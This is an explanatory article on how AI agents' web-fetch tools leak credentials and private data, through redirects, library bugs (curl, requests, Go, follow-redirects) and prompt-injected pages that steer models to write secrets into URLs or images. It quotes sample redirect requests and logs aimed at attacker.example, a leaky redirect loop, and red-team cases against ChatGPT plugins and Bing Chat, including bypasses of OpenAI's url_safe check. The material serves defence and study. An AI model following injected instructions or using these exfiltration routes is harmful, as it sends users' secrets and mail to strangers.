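# Redirect and cross-origin credential attacks on the web-fetch tools of AI agents

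## What a web-fetch tool does and what can be stolen through it

An AI agent is a program in which a language model works on a task by calling tools, which are functions that do something outside the model and return the result to it as text. A web-fetch tool takes a URL from the agent and returns the page's content. Agents use it to read documentation, check a fact or summarise an article for a user.

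The tool's requests often leave from a machine that holds passwords or sits inside a private network. Strangers can influence where these requests go by putting text in a web page that steers the model to another address, or by having a web server answer with a redirect, a response that names another URL to request. Redirect and cross-origin credential attacks use these methods to obtain access tokens, private data or pages that are not reachable from the public internet.

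### One call, step by step

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise the page at `https://docs.example/guide`. The model itself never touches the network. It writes a short structured message with the name of the tool and the URL, and ordinary software does the rest:

1. The tool parses the URL and runs whatever checks its developer built in.
2. It asks the Domain Name System (DNS), the internet's directory of names, for the IP address behind `docs.example`.
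3. It connects to that address. If the URL begins with `https`, it also checks that the server has a valid certificate for `docs.example`.
4. It sends the request: one line with the path, then a set of headers, which are pairs of a name and a value. Most headers describe the client or the wanted format. A credential header, such as `Authorization`, `Cookie` or `X-Api-Key`, proves identity.
5. The server returns a status code, headers of its own and usually a body.
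6. The tool turns the body into plain text and places it in the model's context, the text from which the model produces its next words.

The certificate check in step 3 confirms that the machine is `docs.example`, but it is not evidence that the owner is honest. An attacker can get a valid certificate for `attacker.example`.

Web-fetch tools differ in what they return. *Web fetch tool*, Anthropic's documentation for the version that developers can add to its Claude models, describes a tool that takes only a URL and returns the full text of the page. An average web page of 10 kB takes up about 2,500 tokens (the word fragments in which models process text), and a 500 kB research paper about 125,000. So one fetch can put far more text by a stranger into the context than the user has typed. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, has a different tool, described in *Inside Claude Code's Web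 Tools* (2025), a post on a personal blog whose author inferred part of the behaviour from outside. According to the post, the tool upgrades `http` to `https`, strips any credentials written into the URL, and checks with an Anthropic server whether it may fetch from that host. It then gives the agent an answer to a question about the page instead of the page itself. This probably makes hostile text on the page less effective, though a model still has to read the page to write the answer.

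### URLs, origins and redirects

Most of the safety rules for these tools turn on which part of a URL has changed. Take this one:

```
https://docs.example:8443/guide/setup?lang=en
```

The scheme is `https`, the host `docs.example`, the port `8443`, the path `/guide/setup` and the query `lang=en`. A URL without a port uses the default for its scheme, 443 for `https` and 80 for `http`.

Browsers group URLs by origin, which is the combination of scheme, host and port. Barth (2011), in *The Web Origin Concept*, set out the definition as an internet standard: two URLs share an origin only if all three parts match. Path and query play no role. Measured against `https://docs.example/guide`:

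| URL | What differs | Same origin? |
|---|---|---|
| `https://docs.example:443/guide` | default port, written out | yes |
| `https://docs.example/admin?user=7` | path and query | yes |
| `http://docs.example/guide` | scheme (and default port) | no |
| `https://docs.example:8443/guide` | port | no |
| `https://www.docs.example/guide` | host | no |
| `https://attacker.example/guide` | host | no |

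The definition of an origin includes the scheme because someone on the network can tamper with an unencrypted page. If that page had the same origin as the encrypted version, the attacker could use it to attack the encrypted one. Barth concedes that the origin is still a rough unit. At a university where students publish under `example.edu/~student/`, every student's site has the same origin, so a tool that trusts that origin trusts everyone who can publish there.

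A redirect moves the tool from one URL to another. Here the tool sends a request with a credential header, and the server's reply follows after the blank line:

```
GET /guide HTTP/1.1
Host: docs.example
Authorization: Bearer PLACEHOLDER-SECRET

HTTP/1.1 302 Found
Location: https://attacker.example/landing
```

Status codes that begin with 3 mark redirects, and the `Location` header gives the new address. *HTTP Semantics*, the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) standard for the protocol, allows a client to follow that address automatically, and many HTTP libraries do. Each request in a chain of redirects is called a hop. The second hop here goes to a different host, so the redirect is cross-origin. The tool's HTTP library determines whether that request includes the `Authorization` header.

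The model writes one URL and receives one page, but the software underneath may contact several servers without the model's involvement. If the tool checks only the URL the model wrote, it doesn't check any redirects that follow.

### Prompt injection and the confused deputy

Text on a page can also redirect an agent. Suppose the guide at `docs.example` contains a passage telling AI readers that the guide is incomplete and that the rest is on a page at `attacker.example` whose address must end with the name of the user's city. The passage's author can put it in the page's metadata, where a human visitor may never see it. The tool places the passage in the model's context, a few lines away from the user's request. If the model then calls the tool again with the address described, the city's name is recorded in the attacker's server log. The user gets a decent summary and has no reason to suspect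 anything.

In prompt injection, a model follows instructions in content it reads as if its user had given them. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, compares it with SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types database commands into a web form. Developers can prevent SQL injection completely because a database can keep commands and data apart. A language model has no such separation; it receives one run of text and predicts what comes next. Training a model to favour its user's instructions, or marking web content as data, makes prompt injection harder, but David C doubts that anyone will ever eliminate it completely.

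He proposes treating the model instead as a confused deputy, a program tricked into using its legitimate authority on someone else's behalf. The term comes from operating systems. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a compiler at the timesharing company Tymshare that had permission to write to its own directory, where it kept usage statistics. Users could name a file to receive debugging output. One user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory, and the compiler overwrote it even though the user had no permission to write to that file. Hardy attributed the problem to the compiler drawing authority from two sources with no way to specify which one applied to a given write. His remedy was the capability, a reference that both identifies a file and carries permission to write to it, so that supplying only a file's name gives a user no access.

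An agent with a fetch tool is in much the same position. Its network access and credentials come from the user or developer, but the destination can come from a web page. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) notes that, unlike in the classical case, the uncertainty is over what the user meant, because the agent cannot reliably tell a user's request to fetch a page from an instruction inside that page. David C calls a language model "inherently confusable" for the same reason, whereas the compiler was merely badly designed.

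Lan and colleagues tested an agent built on a small open model, qwen2.5:7b, by giving it the harmless request to summarise a page with instructions hidden in it. Over 480 runs, the agent sent out sensitive data with a probability of about 0.89, and checks on the final answer missed 95% of the successful attacks. The set-up favoured the attacker, because the secrets were in plain view in the context, the system prompt contained little beyond the tool's format, and nothing filtered the page. The 0.89 figure is therefore a poor guide to larger models in guarded products. The 95% figure probably carries over better, because the harm happens in a network request that the answer need not mention.

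Some attacks do not require prompt injection. In the redirect shown earlier, the HTTP library is the deputy because it holds the secret while the remote server supplies the address. Barth describes redirects as "instructions from remote servers", and a library that follows them without adequate checks will leak a credential even if the model is immune to prompt injection.

### Three things to lose

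What an attacker can take falls under three heads, which differ in who picks the destination and where the secret comes from.

An attacker can steal **a credential that the tool attaches to its requests**, such as a key that a developer configured for `docs.example`. The attacker can redirect the tool to their address with a `Location` header from a server they control, or write text that persuades the model to fetch that address. If the tool includes the key in that request, the attacker receives it. Rules about what the model may write or reveal don't prevent this, because the tool adds the key and the model may never have seen it. The protection has to be in the code that decides which headers go to which host.

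**The model can write private data into the URL.** The data comes from the model's context, such as something the user typed, a file the agent opened, or a stored memory of earlier chats. The attacker picks the destination through a hostile page, and the model composes the URL. No credential header is involved, so stripping headers at a redirect doesn't help. The server's response doesn't matter either, because the request has already sent the data. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that visiting a site means sending it the URL, and that sites commonly log the URLs they receive. The HTTP standard similarly warns that URLs "are intended to be shared, not secured".

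Limiting the length of URLs gives only partial protection. Anthropic's tool rejects URLs of more than 250 characters, which still leaves room for a name, an employer and a home town. The researcher Ayush Paul extracted those three facts from Claude's stored memories in an attack that Willison (2026) reported in July. Willison calls the underlying condition the "lethal trifecta", the combination of access to private data, exposure to hostile instructions and a way to send data out. A fetch tool by itself provides the last two.

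A web-fetch tool can expose resources that an attacker cannot reach directly. Companies run wikis, databases and admin pages that accept requests from anyone, but only within the company network. A cloud machine can usually also reach a metadata service, mostly at `169.254.169.254`, that can return the machine's own access tokens. If an attacker uses injected text or a redirect to make the tool request such an address, the internal server returns the secret in its response. Security engineers call this server-side request forgery (SSRF). The attacker needs no stolen credential because the tool's location in the network already gives it access.

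In this last case, the secret first enters the model's context, and the attacker still needs a second step to get it out. That step could be another fetch with the data in the URL, or an answer that the agent posts where the attacker can read it. A defence against the second loss therefore limits the damage from the third, but it cannot undo a request that changed something on the internal server.

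### Three kinds of tool

Which of these losses a given tool can suffer depends mainly on what it carries and where it runs.

| Kind of tool | Attached credential | Private data in the URL | Internal resource |
|---|---|---|---|
| No credentials | not exposed | exposed | exposed if its machine can reach one |
| Fixed credential headers | exposed | exposed | exposed if its machine can reach one |
| Browser with the user's login | attacker can use the login, usually without seeing the cookie | exposed | exposed if its machine can reach one |

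A tool without credentials requests public pages as an anonymous visitor. Attackers may still be able to steal user data through it, because the model that calls it may have access to a great deal of information about the user. The tool may also be able to reach a private network, such as the provider's if it runs on the provider's servers or an employer's if it runs on an employee's laptop. The README on GitHub for a fetch server built on the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting tools to models, includes a warning that the server can access local and internal IP addresses.

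When an agent has to read something behind a login, such as a private code repository or a paid data service, developers add a fixed credential header (`Authorization` or `X-Api-Key`) to the tool's requests. If the tool attaches that header to every request instead of only those to one origin, a single fetch of `attacker.example` sends the attacker the key without a redirect.

Unlike the other fetch tools, a browser stores cookies from the sites where the user has logged in and selects them afresh for each destination, so a redirect from the user's bank to `attacker.example` does not normally send the bank's cookie to the attacker. But an agent that controls such a browser can read the user's mailbox through the logged-in session and then leak what it read through a URL. A June 2026 draft on MCP security, an individual submission to the IETF and not a standard, notes that browser-automation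 servers may run with access to a local browser profile, and that SSRF in one of them reportedly affects both internal services and logged-in sessions. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* describes a check that detects when conversation data is about to reach a third party and either blocks the transmission or asks the user to confirm it. The company applies the same check to page navigation in its Atlas browser, where an ordinary click can send data out just as a fetch can.

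## How browsers and HTTP libraries came to handle redirects, to early 2025

Developers who build web-fetch tools seldom write the redirect handling themselves. They rely on an HTTP library, whose behaviour was shaped by old standards, browser habits and many bug fixes. Library developers could usually assume that a user or a developer had chosen the first URL. They still had to decide what a redirected request should contain, and their decisions differed between libraries.

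### Which redirects resend the body

Every HTTP request begins with a method, which names the kind of action. GET fetches a page. POST sends data, such as the contents of a form, in the request body, and PUT stores the body at the given URL. When a server answers with a redirect, the client has to decide whether to keep the method and body in the next request.

The rules are in section 15.4 of *HTTP Semantics*, which the RFC Editor publishes as RFC 9110. Five status codes matter here:

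| Code | Meaning | A POST becomes | Body sent again? | A PUT in a browser becomes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 301 Moved Permanently | new permanent address | GET in browsers; the standard allows either | only if the method stays POST | PUT |
| 302 Found | temporary address | GET in browsers; the standard allows either | only if the method stays POST | PUT |
| 303 See Other | another page that answers the request | GET | no | GET |
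| 307 Temporary Redirect | temporary address | POST | yes | PUT |
| 308 Permanent Redirect | new permanent address | POST | yes | PUT |

The redirect codes overlap for historical reasons. HTTP/1.0 defined 301 and 302 as codes that preserve the method, to match the software at CERN, and 303 as the code that switches to GET. When a 301 or 302 redirected a POST, some early browsers sent the POST again, as the specification then required, while others sent a GET, which is safer when the redirect leads to a different site. Sending a GET became the usual practice. The standard's editors later changed the definitions of 301 and 302 to permit this, and added 307 and 308 for servers that need the method preserved. Code 308 was introduced only in June 2014, so some old clients may not recognise it.

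For a secret in the body, the choice of code decides everything. Suppose a program logs in to an API like this:

```
POST /token HTTP/1.1
Host: api.example
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded

client_secret=PLACEHOLDER-SECRET

HTTP/1.1 307 Temporary Redirect
Location: https://attacker.example/collect
```

A client that follows this redirect sends the secret to `attacker.example`, because 307 forbids it to change the method, and it resends the body too. Had the server answered with 302, most clients would have sent a GET with no body. The redirecting server picks the code, so the client can't rely on getting a 302. Stripping headers doesn't help, since the secret is in the body. A web-fetch tool that sends only GET requests avoids the problem, but an agent's other tools often call APIs with POST.

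### What the HTTP standard asks of a client

RFC 9110 urges care with automatic redirects when the method can change something on the server. A client that follows a redirect should resend the original request with a few changes. It works out the new URL, adapts the method, and drops headers that describe a body if there is no longer a body. It should also notice when it is going in circles. (An older version of the standard recommended a limit of five redirects, and some clients may still have it.)

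The treatment of the remaining headers depends on who set them. If the client generated a header itself, it should remove it and, where appropriate, generate a new value for the new request. This rule covers `Host`, as well as `Authorization` and `Cookie` when the client looked them up itself. A client that has a stored password for `docs.example` and is redirected to `attacker.example` therefore looks for a password for the new host and doesn't find one.

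The wording is much weaker for headers that the calling program supplied. The client should only "consider removing" them "where there are security implications", with `Authorization` and `Cookie` again as examples. A fixed credential header in an agent's tool falls into this category, because the developer writes the key into a configuration file and the tool passes it to the library.

The standard leaves library developers to decide when a redirect is dangerous. A redirect to a new host surely is, but redirects to a new port, a subdomain, or the same host without encryption are matters of judgement. Developers must also decide which headers are sensitive, because the standard's list is explicitly incomplete. Most of the flaws that library maintainers have fixed since 2018 come from getting one of these two decisions wrong.

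### The browser's version

Browsers follow a stricter text, the WHATWG's Fetch Standard. The WHATWG is the group in which browser makers write many of the web's core specifications. The standard sets out the steps of a request in enough detail that different browsers should behave alike. It also matters outside browsers, because server-side JavaScript systems such as Node.js and Deno offer the same `fetch()` function.

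A program that calls `fetch()` can choose between three redirect modes. In `follow`, the default, the browser follows the chain to its end. In `error`, any redirect makes the request fail. In `manual`, the browser stops at the redirect and returns a response with the details blanked out.

At each redirect in `follow` mode, the browser does roughly this:

1. It resolves the `Location` value against the current URL, and fails if the result is not an `http` or `https` address.
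2. It fails if it has already followed 20 redirects for this request.
3. It changes the method where the table above requires it, and deletes the body and the headers that describe the body.
4. It compares the new URL's origin with the current one. If they differ, it deletes the `Authorization` header.
5. It sends the request to the new URL, with cookies chosen afresh for that address.

Step 4 deletes the header from the request itself, so a later redirect back to the first origin doesn't restore it. The step is fairly new, and some HTTP libraries dropped this header before browsers did. In a comment on the standard's issue tracker, youennf (2016) suggested that custom `Authorization` headers should probably be removed on a cross-origin redirect. Five years later, Paul Millar pointed out in another comment that curl, Python's requests library and Go's HTTP client already dropped the header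 when a redirect led to another host. In November 2022, Anne van Kesteren, who wrote the standard, proposed the change in *Remove Authorization header upon cross-origin redirect* and asked for documentation of it in *Fetch Standard change* (2022). Mozilla adopted it in Firefox 111, according to valentin's ticket, *Remove authorization from fetch on cross origin redirect*.

Some server-side developers complained about the removal of the Authorization header on redirects between hosts, because their programs had relied on it. In a discussion titled *Authorization-removal change was compatibility-breaking*, the reply was that web pages could never rely on the header surviving, so nothing had broken for browsers, though an option to preserve it was conceivable. Some services legitimately redirect requests between hosts, so a library that strips headers by default will break a few legitimate programs.

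The same discussion touched on `manual` mode, which is of little use for checking every hop in a browser because the script cannot see where the redirect leads. Browsers hide the address out of concern about scripts that an attacker has injected into a page. In *URLs of intermediary redirects are leakable in practice (same-origin)*, ukusormus recalls that van Kesteren has compared the sensitivity of a `Location` value with that of an HttpOnly cookie, which scripts cannot read. Login systems, for example, put one-time codes in redirect URLs. One participant in the compatibility dispute asked why server implementations should hide redirects, given that programs there can reportedly read cookies anyway. The objection seems right for an agent's tool, because its code has to see the next address before it can approve or refuse it.

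Before a page's script can send a custom header such as `X-Api-Key` to another origin, the browser sends a preflight, a short request to check that the receiving server accepts the header. This protects the server from requests it never expected, but it doesn't protect the key's owner, because the server at `attacker.example` can accept the header. The browser then sends the key, since step 4 covers only `Authorization`.

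### How a cookie jar picks cookies

A cookie is a small piece of text that a server sends to a client and the client returns with later requests. Most sites use cookies to keep users logged in. The client stores each cookie in a cookie jar, along with the host that set it and any limits the host attached.

Under the WHATWG standard, the browser copies the request before each hop, looks up matching cookies, and adds the `Cookie` header to the copy. The next hop starts from the original request, which never had the header.

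The cookie lookup uses the current URL's host and path and whether its scheme is `https`. If `docs.example` sets a cookie without specifying a domain, the cookie goes back only to `docs.example`. If it specifies `docs.example` as the domain, subdomains such as `www.docs.example` also receive the cookie. A cookie marked Secure is sent only over an encrypted connection. The lookup does not use the port, so a server at `https://docs.example:8443` receives the cookies of `https://docs.example`, although the two are different origins.

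Sites can also mark a cookie SameSite, which restricts its use in requests that another site started. The browser tracks the redirect chain to enforce this. For example, if a request for an image is redirected to another site and back, the browser leaves out cookies with the stricter SameSite settings.

This design is sturdier than stripping because a mistake in it tends to affect unusual domains rather than every redirect. In September 2026, for example, curl disclosed a low-severity flaw in cookies scoped to a domain on the Public Suffix List, a list of domains such as `co.uk` under which unrelated people register names. The flaw went back to version 7.46.0, and version 8.22.0 fixed it.

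None of this helps a program that writes its own `Cookie` header. When a developer copies a session cookie from a browser into a tool's configuration, the cookie becomes an ordinary custom header with no record of the host it belongs to.

### Three libraries, three mistakes

curl is a command-line program and a library (libcurl) that many other applications use to transfer data. Before 2018 it kept credentials that it managed itself to the original host, but it treated an `Authorization` header that the user had typed in as just another custom header. According to curl's *HTTP authentication leak in redirects* (2018), it sent such headers first to the host in the original URL and then to whatever host the `Location` value named. The bug was already in the first commit that the project has on record. Craig de Stigter reported it on 18 January 2018, and six days later version 7.58.0 fixed it.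 The flaw has the number CVE-2018-1000007 in the common catalogue of software vulnerabilities.

After the fix, curl sent a custom `Authorization` header only to the original host. Users can restore the old behaviour on the command line with the option `--location-trusted`. This is sensible because the default is safe and the option's name indicates the risk.

An attacker who wants the key for `docs.example` still has to get `docs.example` to issue the redirect. The attacker could take over the server, but it is far easier to use an open redirect, which is a page on a legitimate site that forwards visitors to any address given in its URL. Sites use such pages to count clicks or to return people to where they were before logging in. When an agent follows a link to an open redirect on `docs.example`, it sends its key to `docs.example`, and an unpatched library then sends the key to the address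 the attacker put in the link.

The Python library requests already dropped the `Authorization` header when a redirect went to another host, but it compared only host names. If `https://docs.example` redirected to `http://docs.example`, the library kept the header and sent it unencrypted, so anyone able to listen on the network could read it. The record *PYSEC-2018-28* in the OSV vulnerability database, published on 9 October 2018, lists version 2.20.0 as the first without this flaw, CVE-2018-18074.

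The curl project rated its own flaw low, while OSV's *CVE-2018-18074* (2018) gives the requests flaw a score of 7.5, or high. For a web-fetch tool, the curl flaw should rank higher, because an attacker can exploit it through an open redirect from anywhere. To exploit the requests flaw, an attacker has to be on the network path to read an unencrypted request.

Go's mistake concerned memory. Its standard HTTP client removed `Authorization` when a redirect crossed to another domain, but the removal didn't last:

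```
hop 1   https://docs.example/          Authorization sent
hop 2   https://attacker.example/1     Authorization removed
hop 3   https://attacker.example/2     Authorization sent again
```

Go's *Vulnerability Report* (2025) describes CVE-2024-45336, a flaw in which the HTTP client dropped sensitive headers when redirected to another domain, then restored them if a second redirect stayed on that domain. An attacker who already controlled the server there needed only to add the second redirect. The project published the report on 28 January 2025 and fixed the client in versions 1.22.11, 1.23.5 and 1.24.0-rc.2. The flaw is a good argument for permanently deleting the header from the request, as browsers do. A developer who tests only a single redirect to another host would miss the flaw, because the header is dropped as expected.

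### Similar flaws in 2025 and 2026

The same kinds of error kept recurring. GitLab's *fetch*, an advisory on CVE-2025-21620, describes how Deno's `fetch()` kept the original `Authorization` header on redirects to a different domain, behaviour that the Fetch Standard had dropped in 2022. Mondoo's *Sensitive headers not cleared on cross-origin redirect in net/http* reports that Go's client kept the `Proxy-Authorization` and `Proxy-Authenticate` headers on cross-origin redirects.

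Several flaws in curl come from how it handles incomplete entries in a `.netrc` file, a plain list of hosts with a user name and password for each, which curl can read to log in. When a redirect leads to a second host, curl checks the file again. Julia's *JLSEC-2026-413* covers CVE-2024-11053, in which curl could send the first host's password to the second if the second host's entry had no password. Julia's *JLSEC-2026-420* covers CVE-2025-0167, in which an empty default entry had the same effect.

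curl's *token leak with redirect and netrc* (2026) describes a third case, which needed no gap in the netrc file. It concerns bearer tokens, which work for whoever holds them. On a redirect, curl could send the first host's token to the second host if the file had any entry that applied to the second host. The project rated this flaw medium and fixed it in version 8.19.0, on 11 March 2026. Two months earlier, curl's *bearer token leak on cross-protocol redirect* (2026) had described a token that leaked on redirects from the web to a mail or directory server, even on the same host, under settings the project considers highly unusual. A single commit introduced both bugs in version 7.33.0.

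A developer who relies on a library's redirect handling therefore relies on a particular version of that library. The errors lasted for years even though these projects are old, widely used and attentively maintained.

### What the rules leave open

Custom credential headers are the largest gap. Many services authenticate callers with `X-Api-Key`, `X-Auth-Token` or a header name of their own, and a library can't distinguish these headers from harmless ones. RFC 9110 recommends that anyone who specifies a new header document whether clients should remove it at a redirect. That advice doesn't cover a company that invents a header for its own API and never writes a specification.

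The JavaScript package follow-redirects, which handles redirects for the very popular HTTP library axios, shows how removing credential headers by name can miss those not on the list. At first it removed `Authorization` and `Cookie`. After a report that `Proxy-Authorization` leaked, the recommended patch, according to GitLab, was to add that name to the list. GCVE's *follow-redirects leaks Custom Authentication Headers to Cross-Domain Redirect Targets* (2026), a copy of an advisory from 14 April, later reported that the package forwarded `X-API-Key` and every other custom credential header unchanged. The US government's vulnerability database, NVD, lists 1.16.0 as the fixed version in its entry *CVE-2026-40895*.

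The advisory suggests either letting developers extend a list of sensitive headers or removing all non-standard headers when a redirect changes domain. An extensible list helps only developers who know they need to extend it. Removing all non-standard headers will break some programs, but developers are more likely to notice a broken program than a leaked key.

The code in that advisory also shows that the package kept all headers when a redirect led to a subdomain of the current host. Browsers treat `files.docs.example` as a different origin from `docs.example`, and at some companies a different team or a customer controls the subdomain.

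Secrets in URLs get even less attention. The `Location` value replaces the old URL, so a query such as `?key=PLACEHOLDER-SECRET` reaches the new host only if the redirecting server copies it across, as servers often do when a site moves to a new hostname. Under the WHATWG standard, the browser carries the fragment, the part of a URL after `#`, over to the new URL unless `Location` has a fragment of its own. Browsers don't send fragments to servers, but a script on the final page can read them. A secret in a fragment is therefore at risk when an agent controls a real browser, but not when it uses a plain web-fetch tool that runs no scripts.

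Finally, a library's rules protect only programs that let the library follow redirects. Developers of agent tools have good reasons to switch this off, for instance to check each address before the tool connects to it. The replacement often looks like this simplified loop:

```python
headers = {"Authorization": "Bearer PLACEHOLDER-SECRET"}
url = "https://docs.example/guide"

for _ in range(5):
    reply = client.get(url, headers=headers, follow_redirects=False)
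    if not reply.is_redirect:
        break
    url = urljoin(url, reply.headers["Location"])
```

The loop limits the number of hops and resolves relative addresses correctly, but it sends the key to every host in the chain. The library treats each pass as a new request with headers supplied by the caller, so there is no redirect at which it could remove the key. Checking the address doesn't prevent this, because `attacker.example` is an ordinary public host.

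Drupal, a widely used system for running websites, had a loop of this kind in its function for outgoing requests. Juraj Nemec's commit in *drupal_http_request() fails to strip Cookie or Authorization headers on HTTP downgrade* added a check before each hop, with a comment citing RFC 9110. The check removes `Cookie` and `Authorization` by name, so the function would still send a key in `X-Api-Key`.

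## From 2023: injected pages that make the model write private data into a URL

In spring 2023, text on a web page could make ChatGPT or Microsoft's Bing Chat write a user's private data into a URL on the attacker's server. Software then requested that URL, which sent the data to the attacker. This was the first data theft that researchers demonstrated on widely used assistants. It needed no redirect or credential header, so even a flawless HTTP library would not have stopped it.

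### One case, from web page to server log

The clearest early case involved two ChatGPT plugins, add-ons through which the model could call outside services. WebPilot fetched web pages. Zapier could read the user's Gmail, because the user had granted it access. In May 2023 the security researcher Johann Rehberger used both to steal an email, which Willison (2023) called the first working proof he had seen of an attack on plugins that took private data. Rehberger's own account on his blog, Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained*, gives the chain of events:

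1. The user asks ChatGPT to open a page, and WebPilot fetches it.
2. The page's text enters the model's context, along with the attacker's instructions.
3. The model follows them and calls Zapier, which returns the user's latest email.
4. The model condenses the email to about 20 words and encodes the result so that it can be part of a URL.
5. The model adds the summary to an address on the attacker's server and calls WebPilot again with that URL.
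6. WebPilot requests the URL, and the attacker's server writes it to its log.

With invented data, the last request and the resulting log entry look like this:

```
GET /note?d=Clinic+moved+your+appointment+to+Friday HTTP/1.1
Host: attacker.example

203.0.113.20 [19/May/2023:10:12:44] "GET /note?d=Clinic+moved+your+appointment+to+Friday" 404
```

The 404 status means that the server has no such page, but the attacker only needs the line in the log.

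Both plugins worked as designed. Zapier read a mailbox with its owner's permission, and WebPilot fetched a public page. Only the model handled both the email and the attacker's address, which makes it the confused deputy. The attacker doesn't have to own the page, since anyone who can add text to it, such as a comment, can inject instructions.

Zapier soon added a confirmation step that the user has to complete while logged in. Rehberger considers the login essential, because an injected page could otherwise have ChatGPT open the confirmation link itself.

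### Loads that nobody clicks

An assistant can leak data this way even if it has no fetch tool. Many assistants write their answers in Markdown, a simple notation for headings, links and images. If an answer contains an image hosted on another server, the user's browser requests the image as soon as it displays the answer. If injected text has made the model write private data into the image's URL, that request sends the data to the server.

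Roman Samoilenko found this flaw in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023. According to Willison (2023), he used a single-pixel image and a web page that added the injected instructions to any text a visitor copied, so that visitors pasted the attack into ChatGPT. Rehberger found the same flaw a few days later. In *ChatGPT Plugins*, he showed that plugins made the pasting unnecessary, because the model could pick up the instructions from a page a plugin had fetched.

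Bing Chat had the flaw too. It could answer questions about the page open in the user's browser, and Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* demonstrates how text on such a page could take control of the chat. The model printed a line announcing the injection, as the text instructed, and the conversation continued for two more turns. The model then produced an image whose URL contained an encoded summary of the page and the chat, including a secret from another part of the page.

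Rehberger also published entries from his own server log in Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*. In one entry from September 2023, the requested URL contains the start of a test chat in readable text, in which the user gives her name as Alice and mentions her interest in finance. Other entries contain only a link. In those tests, the injected text made the model use another plugin to save the whole conversation as a document, diagram or video, then put the link to it in the image URL. This weakens any defence that limits URL length, because a short link can open a long document.

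Messaging apps add another way out. When someone posts a link in Slack, Slack's server fetches the page to show a title and a picture, a feature known as a link preview or unfurling. It does the same for links posted by a chatbot. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* shows the resulting log entry, in which the client's name is `Slackbot-LinkExpanding`. Willison (2024), who had followed these attacks closely, wrote that he hadn't thought of this one before. Developers of Slack apps can prevent it with two settings in each message:

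```
{"text": "...", "unfurl_links": false, "unfurl_media": false}
```

A safe default matters more than the option to turn protection on. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw, an agent used through messaging apps, was exposed in its default Telegram configuration. Adding one line to the configuration file fixes this, but users have to know to add it.

| Channel | What triggers the request | Where the request comes from | Where a defence can act |
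|---|---|---|---|
| Fetch tool | the model calls the tool | the tool's machine | in the tool's code |
| Image in an answer | the app displays the answer | usually the user's browser or app | in the app, before it loads the image |
| Link preview | the agent posts a message | the messaging company's server | in the settings for messages |

A developer who checks only the fetch tool's requests will not see a preview request, because another company's machine sends it.

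### Why the browser's rules do not cover it

Browsers have always let a page load images from other sites. This is reasonably safe because a page's author can normally put into a link only what the author already knows. If someone at `attacker.example` writes an image address, they learn from the request that someone visited, but nothing about the visitor's mail. A script could build an address while the page is open, but the browser doesn't let it read the visitor's mailbox at another origin. Someone who can only leave a plain-text comment can't run a script at all.

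A model removes the separation this assumption depends on. The email, the web page and the user's messages are all in one context, and the model can use any of it when it writes a URL. The attacker supplies a URL with a blank in it, and the model fills the blank with data the attacker has never seen. In the Bing Chat case, a comment was enough to extract a secret from elsewhere on the page, which an ordinary comment can't do in a browser.

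Three common precautions don't help here:

- **Header stripping** had nothing to remove in the email case, since the request went straight to the attacker's server without a credential header.
- **A tool limited to GET** can't send a request body, but the path and query of the URL go out with every GET request. Email text can leave this way in quantity. In January 2026 Willison reported that an injected email had made the assistant Superhuman AI send the contents of dozens of other messages to an attacker's Google Form, which stores data it receives in a GET request.
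- **A tool without credentials** can still leak what the model has read elsewhere. WebPilot had no access to the mailbox, but it sent what the model had obtained through Zapier.

A defence therefore has to check where the URL leads or how the model got it, or else keep private data and hostile text out of the same context. In 2023, Rehberger advised that one plugin should not be able to trigger another by default, especially not one that handles personal data.

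### How Microsoft and OpenAI responded

Rehberger reported the image flaw to Microsoft on 8 April 2023 and to OpenAI the next day. Microsoft told him on 15 June that it had put a fix in place, although he dates the fix to May in a later look back, Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. From outside, he could see that Bing Chat now had a Content Security Policy, a list that a site sends to the browser of the places from which its pages may load content. Simplified, the rule for images was:

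```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src th.bing.com www.bing.com edgeservices.bing.com r.bing.com
```

The browser enforces this list whatever the model writes, and anyone can read it. However, the list also stops Bing Chat from showing images from most of the web. Such a list must also exclude hosts that pass data on to strangers. Superhuman's policy failed because it allowed `docs.google.com`, which hosts Google Forms.

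OpenAI told Rehberger that loading images was a feature and that it planned no changes. Anthropic fixed the same flaw in Claude, according to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*. OpenAI added its first countermeasure in December 2023, more than eight months after Rehberger's report. Before ChatGPT's web page loaded an image, it sent the image's address to an OpenAI service called `url_safe` and showed the image only if the service returned "safe". Willison (2023) found this "a bit weird", since OpenAI could simply have blocked images from outside domains.

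Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes a test on the day the check appeared, in which some images from Rehberger's server still loaded, enough to leak a short word letter by letter. Nobody outside OpenAI knew the criteria, so he couldn't explain why one address passed and a nearly identical one failed. Each app had to call `url_safe` before loading an image, so each needed its own fix. The iPhone app didn't have the check yet, and Rehberger later found that the macOS app lacked it too. A check on OpenAI's servers would have covered every app at once, but he suspects the company put it in the apps so that they could show answers while the model was still writing them.

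Rehberger presented further gaps at Black Hat Europe in 2024. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) describes another, which the security firm had reported in December 2024. The service accepted every `bing.com` link, including links that forward visitors to other sites, and OpenAI had not fixed the problem when Tenable published. Around August 2025, OpenAI changed the check to rely on the company's own index of public URLs. According to Rehberger, this stopped the attacks he had shown at Black Hat, but not the letter-by-letter leak he had described in 2023.

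### How often the attack works: Silent Egress

The 2023 demonstrations showed that the attack was possible but did not measure how often it succeeded. Lan and colleagues measured this in *Silent Egress*, published in February 2026. Their qwen2.5:7b agent automatically fetched a preview of any URL in the user's message and placed up to 500 characters each of the title, description, body and link text in the context, which also contained an invented API key. The user always asked for a summary of the page. The hostile page asked the model to include the key in the URL and described this as a routine connectivity check.

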